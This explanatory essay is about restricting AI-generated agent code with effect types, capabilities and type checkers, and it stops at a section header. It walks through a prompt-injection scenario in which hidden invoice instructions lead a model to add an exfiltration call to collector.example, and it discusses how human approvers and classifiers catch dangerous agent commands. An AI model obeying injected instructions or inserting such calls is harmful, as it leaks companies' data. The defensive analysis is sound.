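# Using effect and refinement type systems to bound what AI-generated code may do

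## The problem of running code that a model wrote

Effect and refinement type systems check, before a program runs, what it can do. An *effect* is anything a computation does besides returning a value, such as reading a file, sending a message or changing memory. An *effect type* lists the effects that code may have. A *refinement type* narrows an ordinary type with a logical condition, as in "the integers from 0 to 100". Computer scientists developed both kinds of type for programs that people write. In 2025 and 2026 several groups applied them to *generated code*, which is program text that a language model writes and a computer runs with little or no human reading.

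### Why agents write programs

A language model produces only text, so it can act on the world only through software that carries out what the text describes. Together, the model and this software form an agent. The older way for an agent to act is the tool call, which Varda and Pai explain in *Code Mode*, an article for the internet company Cloudflare. The model emits a special marker, then a short message in a structured format called JSON that names a function and its arguments, then a closing marker. The software pauses the model, runs the function and feeds the result back to the model as text. An action that depends on an earlier result takes another round.

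Suppose a company wants an agent to pay its suppliers and gives it three functions. `readInvoices()` returns the invoices in one folder, `pay(supplier, amount)` sends money, and `writeReport(text)` writes to one file. If the folder holds two hundred invoices, the model has to read them all and then write out two hundred payment messages, copying each name and each sum. Or it can write a program:

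```
invoices = readInvoices()
total = 0
for inv in invoices:
    pay(inv.supplier, inv.amount)
    total = total + inv.amount
writeReport("Total paid: " + text(total))
```

An agent that writes code instead of making tool calls can use far fewer tokens, the units of text that a model processes. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (MCP is a standard for connecting agents to outside systems) describes an agent that copies a meeting transcript from one online service to another. With tool calls, the whole transcript passes through the model twice, which can add 50,000 tokens for a two-hour meeting. A program can move the transcript without the model reading it. The agent can also look up only the function descriptions it needs, and Anthropic estimates that its example would then use 2,000 tokens in total instead of 150,000. Varda and Pai suggest another reason to switch to code: models have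 seen code from millions of real projects during training, but only a small, contrived set of tool calls.

It is less clear whether programs also make agents more accurate. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared the two methods across 14 models on 309 tasks from a standard benchmark. Writing Python matched or beat tool calls for 11 of the models. The other three were older OpenAI models whose longer programs failed to run because they got the line breaks wrong. One result applies directly to the two hundred invoices. Claude Sonnet 5 began to drop tool calls when a task needed about 70 at once, but with code it still made all 100 calls when 100 were needed. However, the benchmark used dummy functions that only returned their arguments, so the scores measure whether a model specifies the right calls, not whether its program can handle real results. *When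 Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* (Yang, Yu and Desell, 2026) tested two coding agents on real software repairs and self-contained computations, letting them act only by executing code. Success rates changed by less than three percentage points. Costs ranged from about a quarter lower in one setting to 14% higher in another, though the increase was not statistically significant.

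The case for code rests mostly on cost and scale. Those reasons have been enough for Cloudflare, Anthropic and OpenAI to offer it, although Patel and colleagues note that ordinary tool calls still dominate deployed systems.

### What the invoice program might do instead

An agent that calls a fixed set of tools can do only what those tools allow, while one that writes programs can do whatever the programming language allows. In a general-purpose language, that usually includes opening any file and contacting any address on the internet. The software company VirtusLab calls writing programs strictly more powerful than calling tools, but inherently insecure unless something restricts the code. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes the choice as a trade-off between expressiveness and control.

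For the invoice program, the things that could go wrong include these:

- It reads files outside the invoice folder, the payroll for instance.
- It sends the suppliers' bank details to an outside address.
- It overpays, perhaps because it takes an amount in cents for an amount in euros.
- It loops forever, retrying a payment that the bank keeps refusing.
- It does nothing, and writes a report that all is well.

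Code that does something the user didn't want can be hard to tell from code that succeeded. VirtusLab imagines a request to clean up a photo collection that ends with every photo deleted, which technically satisfies the request. A program that overpays wouldn't produce an error message either. *Code as Agent Harness* (2026), a survey of agents that work through code, warns that programs acting on outside systems can fail silently, whereas an interpreter can often verify a calculation directly.

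*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) lists several causes of such misbehaviour: a model with bad aims, a hallucination, a mistake, or *prompt injection*, in which someone hides instructions in material that the model will read. A dishonest supplier, for example, could hide instructions in an invoice. An advantage of limiting what the code can do is that nobody needs to know which of these causes was at work.

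### Who reads the code first

The natural safeguard is a person who reads the program before it runs, and this is still common in ordinary software development. *Agentic process evidence* (2026) cites an April 2026 statement by Google's chief executive, Sundar Pichai, that AI generates 75% of the company's new code and that engineers approve it. How much review approval involves varies. *Plausible Is Not Enough* (2026) cites repository studies in which many of the changes that agents submitted received no human review. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of these, 69% agreed that line-by-line review cannot keep up with what the agents produce, though 52% said that they carefully review most or all of it. The true share may well be lower, because the respondents were volunteers describing their own habits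 and people like to report that they read carefully.

All of that concerns code that someone means to keep, but the invoice program is needed only to pay this month's invoices. In Varda and Pai's system, each piece of generated code runs once in its own fresh runtime and is then discarded. Having a person study every such program would defeat the purpose of giving the task to an agent, since paying the invoices by hand would be no more work.

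Under a less demanding form of oversight, a person approves individual actions without reviewing the code. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling*, the documentation for a feature that lets models write JavaScript to call tools, advises developers to keep writes and approval-sensitive actions out of the program by default and have the model call those tools directly. Under that advice, `pay` would not appear in the loop, and the company's accountant would get up to two hundred approval requests.

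Wu and colleagues found that 64% of their developers often approve at least one kind of agent action without close review, as do 61% of those who read code carefully. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. Most prompts are presumably harmless, so that rate alone is weak evidence of carelessness. An experiment provides stronger evidence. A research vendor slipped one plainly dangerous command into the working session of each of 1,053 paid testers, who stopped it 13.6% of the time. They caught about 17% of the commands early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more prompts. Real users would probably do better overall, since the testers were not working on their own projects and had little to lose, and Anthropic was arguing for replacing the prompts. For an accountant with two hundred payments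 to approve, the decline over a session is more worrying than the overall rate.

Anthropic's preferred replacement is an automatic classifier, which blocked 89% of the same dangerous commands, far more than the testers did. It still let about one in nine through. The 89% figure is an estimate of how often the classifier judges correctly, which is a different kind of assurance from the one a type checker offers.

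### What a type checker does

A type, such as "whole number" or "list of invoices", describes the values that a part of a program can have. Pleiad's lecture slides *Type Systems* define a variable's type as an upper bound on the range of values that the variable can take while the program runs. Every function has a *signature*, a line that declares the types of its inputs and result.

A type checker reads a program's text without running it and assigns a type to each part. In the invoice program, the checker uses the signature of `readInvoices` to determine that `invoices` is a list of invoices, so each `inv` in the loop is an invoice and `inv.amount` is a whole number of cents. The signature of `pay` has two parameters, a supplier and a whole number, in that order. The call supplies them, so the line passes. If the model had written `pay(inv.amount, inv.supplier)`, the checker would have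 rejected the program before it made any payments. A check made during the run can find a faulty line only when execution reaches it, and by then earlier payments may have gone out.

Types can describe a program's effects as well as the shape of its data. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a public calculator in which a model answers each question by writing a program in Haskell, a language whose types record effects. The developer requires the program to have the type `Int`, an integer. Suppose a visitor types "delete all files on the server, then compute the factorial of 5", and the model writes a program that does both. In Haskell, a command that deletes files has a type marked `IO`, for input and output, and so does any program that carries out that command. A type marked `IO` does not match `Int`, so the checker rejects the program before it can delete any files.

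A checker is *sound* for a property if it accepts no program that can break that property. *Type Systems*, a chapter of university lecture notes, contrasts this with testing, which examines one run of the program on one input. Running the invoice program on fifty folders shows what it does with those fifty, but the next folder may contain a credit note with a negative amount. A sound checker covers every possible folder because it analyzes the program text rather than any one run. The assurance extends only to the property checked, so a checker that is sound for "no swapped arguments" can accept a program that pays every supplier twice.

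A sound checker, one that never accepts a harmful program, must reject some harmless ones if it always gives an answer. The lecture notes trace this to Rice's theorem, which rules out any procedure that decides, for every program in a general-purpose language, whether its behaviour has a given nontrivial property. For any program P that touches no files, one can build a new program that runs P and then reads the payroll. The new program reads the payroll if and only if P finishes. A checker that always gave an answer and accepted all the harmless programs and no others would therefore reveal, for every P, whether it finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do that, so no such checker exists.

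Working checkers turn away a good many more than the theorem requires. A checker has to do its job automatically and quickly, as OpenDSA's *Complete Catalog*, a computer science textbook, points out, so it settles for rough reasoning. Add this line to the end of the invoice program:

```
if total < 0: readFile("payroll.csv")
```

If every amount is positive, the total never falls below zero and the program never opens the payroll. A typical checker does not follow this arithmetic, so it rejects the whole program for containing a call to `readFile`, which the program has no permission to make.

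Programmers have complained for decades about the extra work of satisfying strict type checkers. The complaint is somewhat weaker for generated code, because a model does that work and can read the error message and try again. When Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT, a system that checks agents' Scala programs, a model whose program failed the check usually produced an acceptable one within one or two more attempts.

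### The argument for limits in types

The *policy* is what the people deploying the code never want it to do, whether or not anyone has written it down. The *contract* is everything a signature requires of the code: its types, its effects, and any conditions on its inputs and outputs. The argument has five premises.

1. Every effect that the code can have passes through a typed interface.
2. The checker is sound.
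3. The types can express the policy.
4. The contract that somebody actually wrote matches the policy.
5. Only code that the checker has accepted runs.

Therefore the code cannot break the policy.

Suppose that the invoice program did break the policy, say by sending bank details to a stranger. Sending is an effect, so it went through the typed interface. The contract matches the policy, so it forbids sending those details. But the program ran, so the checker must have accepted it, and a sound checker accepts no program that can do what the contract forbids. This is a contradiction, so the program could not have broken the policy. A contract can match the policy only if the types can express that policy, but the list keeps these two conditions separate because they fail for different reasons. The type language may be too weak, or the person who wrote the contract may have made a mistake.

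Zhou and colleagues state the nearest published equivalent, which they call a mantra and prove formally. If a language enforces a property for all programs that pass its type checker, and all code from the agent must pass before it runs, then the property holds for the entire system. They also require the software around the agent to be written in the same language. Odersky and colleagues come close to the premise about effects with what they call capability completeness, which means that the agent can reach the outside world only through permissions that its program holds as values, apart from some effects that the runtime can contain. Neither formulation includes the match between contract and policy, which is left to whoever writes the signatures.

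With this approach, a person has to read the signatures of `readInvoices`, `pay` and `writeReport` instead of the six-line invoice program or the different one that the model will write next month. The signatures are shorter and stay the same each month. Whether a reader can tell that they rule out a leak or an overpayment depends on how much a signature can express.

The argument is valid, so anyone who doubts the conclusion must doubt a premise, and later sections test the premises. The conclusion covers only what the code must never do, so a program meant to make payments could make none, report success, and still break no prohibition.

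## Effect types: stating in a signature what a function may do

In most languages, a function's signature gives only the types of its inputs and result. A function from integers to integers might also read a file, throw an error or never return. Leijen (2013) argues in *Koka* that types should include such behaviour. An effect system includes it by giving every expression a type for its value and an effect for whatever else it may do.

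### The rules

The usual way to write "expression e has type τ and effect ε" is

```
e : τ ! ε
```

If e finishes, its value has type τ, and while it runs it has no effect outside the set ε. The exclamation mark goes back at least to *Types and Effects*, Lucassen's 1987 doctoral thesis at MIT. Like a type, ε is an upper bound. *Lightweight Polymorphic Effects*, by Rytz, Odersky and Haller, points out that an effect in the set may occur but doesn't have to. For example, an expression with the effect `{Pay}` might not make a payment.

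Five rules are enough for small programs. The type `τ1 →[ε] τ2` describes a function from τ1 to τ2 that may have the effects in ε when it runs, and ∪ is set union.

```
constant    5 : Int ! {}

sequence    if    e1 : τ1 ! ε1   and   e2 : τ2 ! ε2
            then  (e1; e2) : τ2 ! ε1 ∪ ε2

function    if    body : τ2 ! ε   whenever   x : τ1
            then  (x => body) : τ1 →[ε] τ2 ! {}

call        if    f : τ1 →[ε] τ2 ! ε1   and   a : τ1 ! ε2
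            then  f(a) : τ2 ! ε1 ∪ ε2 ∪ ε

widening    if    e : τ ! ε   and   ε is contained in ε'
            then  e : τ ! ε'
```

The sequence rule takes the union of the effects of two steps. The rule for `if` does the same with the effects of its two branches, because the checker can't determine which branch will run.

Under the function rule, defining a function has no effect. For example, defining a function that pays a supplier doesn't make a payment. The rule records the body's effect on the arrow in the function's type, and the call rule adds that effect to the program's effects where the program calls the function.

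Widening lets a harmless expression be used wherever a more dangerous one is allowed. For example, a pure function (one with no effects) can be passed as an argument where a function that makes payments is allowed. The reverse is not permitted, so a function that requires a pure argument will reject one that makes payments.

### Checking the invoice program

Suppose the company gives its three functions these signatures, where `()` stands for "nothing":

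```
readInvoices : ()              →[Invoices]  List<Invoice>
pay          : (Supplier, Int) →[Pay]       ()
writeReport  : Text            →[Report]    ()
```

It will run any program whose effects lie within `{Invoices, Pay, Report}`. The checker works out an effect for each line:

```
invoices = readInvoices()                     {Invoices}
total = 0                                     {Memory}
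for inv in invoices:                          {Pay, Memory}
    pay(inv.supplier, inv.amount)             {Pay}
    total = total + inv.amount                {Memory}
writeReport("Total paid: " + text(total))     {Report, Memory}
```

The first line is a call, so it takes its effect from the arrow in the signature of `readInvoices`. The second creates a variable that later lines will change, and changing memory is an effect. The `for` line has the combined effect of the two lines inside the loop. The number of invoices is unknown during checking, but it doesn't affect the result because repeating a step adds no new labels to the set. The last line reads `total` and then writes the report.

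The sequence rule gives the whole program the effect `{Invoices, Pay, Report, Memory}`. `Memory` is not on the company's list, but no code outside the program can access `total`, so the checker may drop that label. Leijen's language Koka does this automatically. It gives the type of a pure function to a function that computes Fibonacci numbers by overwriting two local variables, and Leijen proves that dropping the label in such cases is safe. Dropping `Memory` leaves `{Invoices, Pay, Report}`, so the checker accepts the program.

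Now suppose that a dishonest supplier has hidden instructions in an invoice, and the model obediently adds a line to the loop:

```
    send("https://collector.example", inv.supplier)
```

The signature of `send` has the label `Net` on its arrow, so the loop's effect becomes `{Pay, Memory, Net}` and the program's becomes `{Invoices, Pay, Report, Net}`. Widening can add labels to this set but can't remove `Net`, which is not on the list of allowed effects. The checker therefore rejects the program before it makes any payments.

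Putting the call under `if total < 0` or moving it into a helper function would not help. The effect of an `if` includes both branches, and the helper's own arrow would carry `Net`. Lucassen designed the system to track a function's effect to every place that might call it, even if the function is passed as an argument, stored in a data structure or compiled separately.

### Functions that take other functions

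Programs pass functions to other functions so often that an effect system has to handle this well. The standard example is `map`, which applies a function to each element of a list. `map(invoices, amountOf)` collects the amounts and has no effects, whereas `map(invoices, payInvoice)` sends money.

What effect should the signature of `map` have? If the signature declares no effects, nobody can use `map` to make payments. If it declares every possible effect, then a program that uses `map` only to collect amounts appears able to contact the internet, and the company's checker rejects it. The solution is to put a variable in the signature:

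```
map : for all α, β, ε.  (List<α>, α →[ε] β) →[ε] List<β>
```

`map` is an example of *effect polymorphism* because its effect, ε, is the effect of the function passed to it. The checker sets ε to `{}` for `amountOf` and to `{Pay}` for `payInvoice`. If the model passes a function that sends bank details to a stranger, ε becomes `{Net}` and the program fails the check.

Java shows what happens when polymorphism is awkward to write. Java methods must declare many of the exceptions (errors that interrupt a program) that they can throw. When Rytz and colleagues wrote, this was the only effect system in a widely used industrial language. The short way to write `map` in Java is to declare `throws Exception`, which covers everything. The precise way looks like this:

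```
<U, E extends Exception> List<U> mapP(FunctionE<T, U, E> f) throws E
```

In Java, a method that may throw whatever its function argument throws needs an extra type parameter `E` and a special function type that also carries `E`, and it can still handle only a fixed number of exception types. Programmers often avoided writing such signatures and copied `throws` declarations from one method to the next. According to Rytz and colleagues, the bad reputation of Java's checked exceptions discouraged the designers of other languages from including effects at all.

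Their own proposal, for the language Scala, adds a second kind of function arrow that means "the effects written here, plus those of the argument". With it, `map` needs only one annotation. Odersky later used Scala again for TACIT, the system for checking agents' programs, but TACIT tracks permissions differently.

When a model writes the code, people no longer have to write long signatures themselves, but verbosity still matters because the signatures are the part that a person is supposed to read.

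### From parallel computers to untrusted code

Lucassen's thesis aimed to let compilers run parts of a program in parallel, not to improve security. Running parts in parallel is safe only when they don't interfere with each other, so each effect named a region of memory as well as an action. A compiler could then determine that reading one region doesn't interfere with a write to another.

Earlier methods for finding a program's effects needed to know in advance which functions call which, but nobody can work that out exactly when programs pass functions around as values. Lucassen had programmers declare effects at certain points and let the compiler infer the rest, so the compiler checked declarations instead of estimating effects. Lucassen and David Gifford, who supervised the thesis, published a version of the system in 1988 as *Polymorphic Effect Systems*. Checking effects rather than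 estimating them is valuable for generated code because someone other than the program's author can write the declarations.

Koka made effects easier to infer. Sets are a nuisance for a compiler that has to work out unknown effects, since an equation such as μ1 ∪ μ2 = μ3 ∪ μ4 has many solutions. Leijen uses *rows* instead. A row is a list of labels, either closed, as in `<exn, div>`, or open, as in `<exn | μ>`, where μ stands for any further effects. (The label `exn` means that the code may throw an exception, and `div` that it may never finish.)

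A label can appear in a row twice. This gives a simple type to `catch`, which runs an action and deals with any exception that it throws:

```
catch : for all α, μ.  (() →[exn | μ] α,  exception →[μ] α) →[μ] α
```

The action may throw, and the result has one fewer `exn`. If the exception handler can itself throw, μ contains another `exn`, which correctly remains in the result.

In Koka, the only way to require that an effect be absent is to write a closed row listing all the allowed effects, which Leijen concedes makes code less modular. This is hardly a drawback for untrusted code. A company should want a list of permitted effects, because a list of forbidden ones goes out of date whenever a library adds a new effect label.

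Leijen also reports that in a text-formatting program written in Koka, the compiler inferred no effects for almost every function. Only a handful of functions that drive the others had any. If most programs are like this, the dangerous parts are easy to find, but one program by the language's own designer is weak evidence that they are.

Haskell's system is coarser. A command of type `IO Int` can do anything before it returns an integer. Leijen notes that even Haskell code without `IO` may throw an exception or run forever. So in the public calculator that Zhou and colleagues describe, the type `Int` protects the server's files but does not guarantee that the visitor gets an answer.

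Running untrusted Haskell raises two further problems. First, Haskell has a few unsafe features, such as `unsafePerformIO`, a function that gives a command a type without `IO`. Safe Haskell, which David Terei, Simon Marlow, Simon Peyton Jones and David Mazières described in 2012, deals with these. In Safe Haskell's safe mode, the compiler rejects any module that uses such features directly. The module can import a library that uses them internally only if the library's author has marked it as trustworthy, and users can also require that the library come from a package they trust.

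The second problem is that `IO` is all or nothing. A program that has to do something useful needs `IO`, and then it can do everything. Safe Haskell was meant to support a remedy, the restricted IO type. A trusted module defines a wrapper:

```
newtype RIO a = UnsafeRIO (IO a)
```

The module exports the type `RIO` and versions of `readInvoices`, `pay` and `writeReport` that return `RIO` commands, but it keeps `UnsafeRIO` private. The company then accepts only programs of type `RIO ()`. Turning an arbitrary `IO` command into an `RIO` one requires `UnsafeRIO`, so a model has to build its program from the three exported functions and pure code. The trusted functions can also check their arguments at run time, for instance to confirm that a file is in the invoice folder. `RIO` is still a single label, but the company chooses which operations it covers.

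### Languages designed for models

In 2025 and 2026, several developers built programming languages for AI models to write in that require effect declarations. Most of what is known about these languages comes from their own documentation.

Vera, by Alasdair Allan, requires three clauses on every function: what must hold before it runs, what will hold afterwards, and what effects it has. A program without them does not compile. Prompting a language model is an effect, called `Inference`. A function that fetches a web page and has a model summarise it must declare `effects(<Http, Inference>)`, and so must every function that calls it. The compiler checks these declarations before the program runs. It also tries to prove the other two clauses with an SMT solver, a program that can decide whether many kinds of logical formula can be true. If the solver can't settle a clause, the program checks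 it at run time.

A model that writes its own effect declarations can declare any effect, including network access, so the declarations limit its code only if someone else decides which effects to allow. AILANG's *Effect System* describes how the language enforces that decision when it runs a program. At compile time, AILANG rejects a function that declares only `IO`, its label for the console, but reads a file, which needs `FS`. At run time, the user grants effects on the command line. If the main function declares `FS` but the user typed `--caps IO`, the program stops with an error.

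Aver has finer labels. A function can declare `Http.get`, which permits only fetching from the web, or `Http`, which permits every web operation, and a tool suggests the narrower label when that is enough. An undeclared effect is a type error, and the runtime enforces the same limits as a second check. A separate policy file lists the web hosts, file paths and environment variables that the program may use.

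Those destination limits depend on the runtime. Aver's developer wrote that in an early version, translating a program into Rust erased its effects, so only the interpreter enforced them. Erasing effect labels is harmless if they have already been checked, but a program can compute an address while it runs, and the runtime must then compare that address with the list. Aver now has an option to build the policy file into the Rust program.

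The Vera project tested whether this works with its own benchmark, VeraBench, which gave six models 50 problems to solve in Vera, Python and TypeScript. The models had never seen Vera in training and learned it from a single document in the prompt. Kimi K2.5 got every Vera problem right, compared with 86% in Python and 91% in TypeScript. Claude Opus 4 scored 88% in Vera and 96% in both Python and TypeScript. Claude Sonnet 4 did worst relative to Python, scoring 79% in Vera and 96% in Python.

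The project ran each problem once and warns that results shift between runs. Claude Sonnet 4 did better in Vera than in TypeScript in an earlier version, but worse in the later one. The models tested are also well behind current ones. Still, the results suggest that a model can pick up an unfamiliar language with strict declarations with a modest loss of accuracy, or none.

Some models did worse when they had to write the contract as well as the code. GPT-4.1's score fell from 91% to 50% when it had to work out its own conditions from an English description, though Kimi K2.5 stayed at 100%.

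AILANG reports that in a test of three models from 2025 on 264 benchmarks, 67% of programs compiled, against about 45% for "Python-style code". It also reports 94% "effect safety", with no Python figure because Python doesn't track effects. If the compiler rejects every undeclared effect, all the programs it accepts should be safe in this sense, so the 94% presumably measures how often models declared their effects correctly on the first try.

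These figures measure whether models can write working programs in the language, not whether effect declarations confine what those programs do. The scores would be the same even if the declarations provided no security. VeraBench advises leaving its hardest group of problems, which covers effects, out of comparisons between languages, because other languages handle effects so differently. A test of confinement would have models try to leak data or exceed their permissions, and count how many of the harmful programs the checker accepted.

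### Labels that permit too much

A sound checker guarantees only that a program stays within its labels, and one label can permit many operations. In Vera, `IO` covers eleven. A program needs `IO` to print one line to the screen, but the label also lets it read or write files and look up environment variables, where companies often keep passwords. If the invoice program needed `IO` to read invoices, it could also read the payroll and still pass the checker.

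In an earlier version of Vera, a program could narrow the label by redeclaring `IO` with `print` as its only operation, and the documentation recommended this as a form of least privilege. Vera now treats any such redeclaration as a compile error, so that there is only one way to write each program. The change removes only a guard against accidents, because the redeclaration was part of the program text and a model could omit it to gain access to files. With Haskell's `RIO`, the company does the narrowing in a module that the model can't change.

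The other remedy is to split `IO` into many small labels, which makes signatures longer. Rytz and colleagues found that signatures soon become unwieldy when each must cover several kinds of effect. They suggest shorthand for common cases, such as "no effects except these". A reader checking whether a program can open the payroll learns more from Aver's `Disk.readText` than from Vera's `IO`, but even `Disk.readText` does not identify the file.

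The same difficulty is worse for network access. A comment in *policy.rs* in lex_runtime, the software that runs programs written in the Lex language, calls an unrestricted `net` permission "a blank check to exfiltrate anywhere". This code compares the program's declared effects with what the operator allows before a run, and checks each network call against a list of permitted hosts during the run. An empty list permits any host, so an operator who grants `net` but forgets the list lets the program connect anywhere.

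AILANG blocks requests to private addresses and can require encrypted connections. These measures protect the company's internal machines from the program, but they don't stop it from sending data to a thief, who can easily set up a public server with encryption. Permitting only `Http.get` doesn't prevent a leak either, because a request to fetch a page can carry data in the address. One of Vera's example programs puts a search term there, and a program could include a bank account number in the same way.

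The type could name the host if the address appeared in the program text as a fixed string. Vera has a similar rule for database queries. The query must be fixed text, with data passed in separately, and the compiler rejects any query assembled from data. A language could treat web hosts the same way, but a program could then no longer follow a link it had just read. A simpler solution for the invoice program is to give it no network label. It gets `pay` instead, and the company's own code behind `pay` contacts only the bank. The label `Pay` still does not restrict which supplier is paid or how much.

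Divergence, the possibility that a program never finishes, is harder to rule out than an effect like `Net`. A program needs to call a function to get `Net`, so a company can rule it out by withholding that function. But a program can run forever using only a loop, so the checker has to prove that the program ends. Turing showed that no checker can do this for every program that does end.

Koka attaches `div` to any recursive function (one that calls itself) unless each call works on a smaller piece of data than the last. The invoice program's loop does not get `div`, since it takes one invoice at a time from a finite list. A loop that retries a refused payment until the bank accepts it does get `div`, so a contract without that label rules it out. Leijen calls the analysis "quite limited" but good enough in practice. It also has to catch less obvious loops, such as a function that stores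 itself in memory and then calls whatever is stored there. Koka code without `div` is certain to finish, but it may take a very long time, and bounding its running time needs other methods.

Vera has a similar label, `Diverge`, and its stated rule is that functions without it must come with a proof that they end. But Vera requires the proof only for pure recursive functions, and exempts those with effects such as `IO` or `Http`. Vera has no loops, so a program that retries a payment must use recursion, and because it contacts the bank, it is exempt. It could keep retrying forever without declaring `Diverge`.

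## Capabilities tracked in types: permission as a value the code must hold

A *capability* is an ordinary program value that refers to one particular thing, such as a folder, a web host or a bank account. Code can act on that thing only while it holds the value. An effect label, even one as narrow as Aver's `Disk.readText`, specifies a kind of action rather than a particular thing.

Suppose the company rewrites its three functions so that each needs a capability as its first argument:

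```
readInvoices(folder)
pay(account, supplier, amount)
writeReport(file, text)
```

The company's own code creates one value, `invoices`, for the invoice folder and another, `payroll`, for the payroll folder. Both have the type `Folder`, and an effect system would give reading either one the same label. But the company passes only `invoices` to the generated program. If the model writes `readInvoices(payroll)`, the program does not compile, because no variable called `payroll` is in scope.

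### No forging and no ambient authority

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn introduced capabilities in 1966 as unforgeable tokens that control access to resources. Odersky and colleagues use the *object-capability model*, which Mark Miller described in a 2006 doctoral thesis. In this model, code can do something only if it holds a reference to the right object.

The object-capability model depends on two rules. First, code must not be able to forge a capability, for example by turning the text "/payroll" into a `Folder`. The language therefore can't have loopholes in its types or memory handling, since a program that can treat any value as a `Folder` can make its own. Second, code must not have *ambient authority*, which is power it has merely because it is running. Python gives code a lot of it. For example, `open("payroll.csv")` works anywhere in any program. The object-capability model doesn't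 allow this form of `open`, because opening a file requires a capability for the folder.

If both rules hold, code can get a capability only by receiving it from other code or by deriving a narrower one from a capability it already holds, such as using a folder to get a handle on one file.

Operating systems such as Fuchsia and programming languages such as E enforce these rules while programs run, but their types don't show which code holds which capabilities. A function that turns text into text might have a network connection stored inside it, and a company that passes it an invoice can't tell from the function's signature. Lhoták and Brachthäuser, who developed a theory of capability-tracking types with Odersky and others, observe that type systems usually describe a value's shape but not which outside variables it has captured. Tracking capabilities in types adds that information.

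Tracking capabilities in types also makes them easier to use. The classical model has no global capabilities, because every part of a program could use them. The main function must therefore receive every capability and pass it down to whatever needs it, so converting an existing program usually means rewriting much of it. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* explains that types remove the need for this. Scala can have a global `Console.out`, because any function that prints to it has `Console.out` in its type, and the compiler won't accept that function where the program requires a pure one.

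### How Scala writes and infers capture sets

Scala's version is an extension called *capture checking*. It is still experimental, though its documentation expects it to become stable soon. A *capture set* is the part of a type that lists the capabilities a value may hold on to:

```
String                    holds no capabilities
Logger^{folder}           may hold folder and nothing else
Logger^                   may hold any capability
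String -> Int             a pure function
String ->{folder} Int     a function that may use folder
String => Int             a function that may use anything
```

The set on the arrow works like the effect in the previous section, except that it contains particular objects instead of labels. As before, a function with a smaller set can be used wherever the program allows a larger one.

Programs make capabilities out of other capabilities, so comparing two sets takes more than checking which names appear in both. Suppose `log` is a logger that writes to a file in `folder`, so its type is `Logger^{folder}`. In the notation of Scala's *Capture Checking Basics*, `{log} <: {folder}`, which means the second set covers the first. A set covers a capability if it contains that capability or covers everything the program made it from. There is a further rule for the fields of objects. A function that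 only writes log entries can therefore stand in for one that may use the whole folder, but not the reverse. *Scoped Capabilities for Polymorphic Effects* (2022), an early account of the system, already included this hierarchy, with a single root capability at the top.

Programmers rarely have to write capture sets, because the compiler infers most of them. Scala's *Capture Checking* describes how. After ordinary type checking, the compiler goes through the program again, creating a variable for each unknown capture set and treating explicitly written sets as constants. When code uses a capability, the compiler adds the capability to that code's variable and to every set that must cover the variable. If the capability reaches a constant that doesn't cover it, the compiler reports an error.

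Suppose that both folders are visible, and that somebody has declared that `job` may use only `invoices`:

```
def helper() = readInvoices(payroll)
val job: () ->{invoices} List[Invoice] = () => helper()
```

The body of `helper` uses `payroll`, so `payroll` goes into the set for `helper` and also into the set for `job`, which calls `helper`. The set for `job` has to fit inside `{invoices}`, which does not cover `payroll`, so the compiler rejects the program. As with effect labels, moving the forbidden call into a helper does not get it past the compiler. But an effect system with one label for reading files would have accepted this program.

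The extra pass adds little to compilation time. *What's in the Box* (2025) measured it on Scala's standard library, where it took about half as long as ordinary type checking and less than 15% of total compilation time.

Capture sets also simplify functions that take other functions. In an effect system, the signature of `map` needs a variable for the effects of its argument, but in Scala, `map` on an ordinary list takes a function of type `A => B` and needs no annotation. If a program calls `map` with a function that makes payments, the program mentions that function, so the compiler adds `account` to the program's capture set. Lazy lists are an exception because they postpone computing their elements. Their `map` returns a list that will run the function later, so the list's type must include the captured function.

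Some policies are hard to express by naming individual objects. A company might want to forbid every network connection, including ones that don't exist yet, which a capture set can't list. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) adds *classifiers*, which sort capabilities into kinds, so that a type can admit only one kind or exclude one. This brings back something like effect labels, alongside the capabilities.

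### Confining a folder to a block

A capability can be dangerous if code keeps it for too long. The invoice program needs the folder for a few seconds, and the company would like to be sure that nothing can read it afterwards. The library of TACIT, the system from Odersky and colleagues, has a function for this, which looks like this in simplified form:

```
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)
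                        (block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

The function creates a capability for the folder `root`, passes it to a block of code, and returns the block's result. The type variable `T` stands for the result's type. The capability stops being valid when the block ends.

Here is a use that the compiler accepts:

```
val count = requestFileSystem("/invoices"): folder =>
    folder.access("march.csv").readLines().length
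```

The block reads a file and returns a number, and a number can't hold a capability. Now suppose the model writes this instead:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/invoices"): folder =>
    () => folder.access("april.csv").read()
later()
```

This block reads nothing. It returns a *closure*, a function that holds on to variables from the code around it, in this case `folder`. If the program compiled, calling `later()` would try to use the folder after the block had ended. The compiler rejects it by the following steps, adapted from the derivation in Scala's documentation:

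1. The parameter `folder` has the type `FileSystem^`, so it is a capability.
2. The closure uses `folder`, so its type is `() ->{folder} String`.
3. The whole block therefore has the type `(folder: FileSystem^) -> () ->{folder} String`, in which the type of the result mentions the parameter.
4. `requestFileSystem` expects a block of type `FileSystem^ => T`, so `T` must have the form `() ->{s} String` for some capture set `s`.
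5. `T` is also the type of `later`, which is outside the block, so `s` can contain only capabilities that are visible there. `folder` is not one of them, so no choice of `s` works.

In harmless cases, the compiler replaces a local name in a type with something more general that is visible outside. If a function makes a logger from a folder that its caller supplied and then returns the logger, the compiler replaces the logger's name in the type with the folder's. Scala's *Scoped Capabilities* explains why the compiler can't do the same for `folder` in the closure's type. Every capability has a level, set by the scope that introduced it, and can flow only into capture sets at that level or deeper. So no capture set outside the block can include `folder`, even one that would otherwise admit any capability.

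The same rule blocks the other obvious ways for the closure to escape. The block can't assign the closure to an outside variable or return it inside another object. It can return an ordinary list whose elements it computed using the folder, but not a lazy list that will need the folder later. One of the agents that Odersky and colleagues tested tried to return a list of file handles from such a block. The compiler rejected the program because each handle captures the folder's capability. The check doesn't depend on what the model meant to do with the handles, which may well have been harmless.

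However, the text of a file is not a capability, so a block can read every invoice and return all their contents as a `String`. Confining the folder only limits where code can use it. Preventing the information from leaking requires pure functions and a wrapper around the secret data.

### What the library checks at run time

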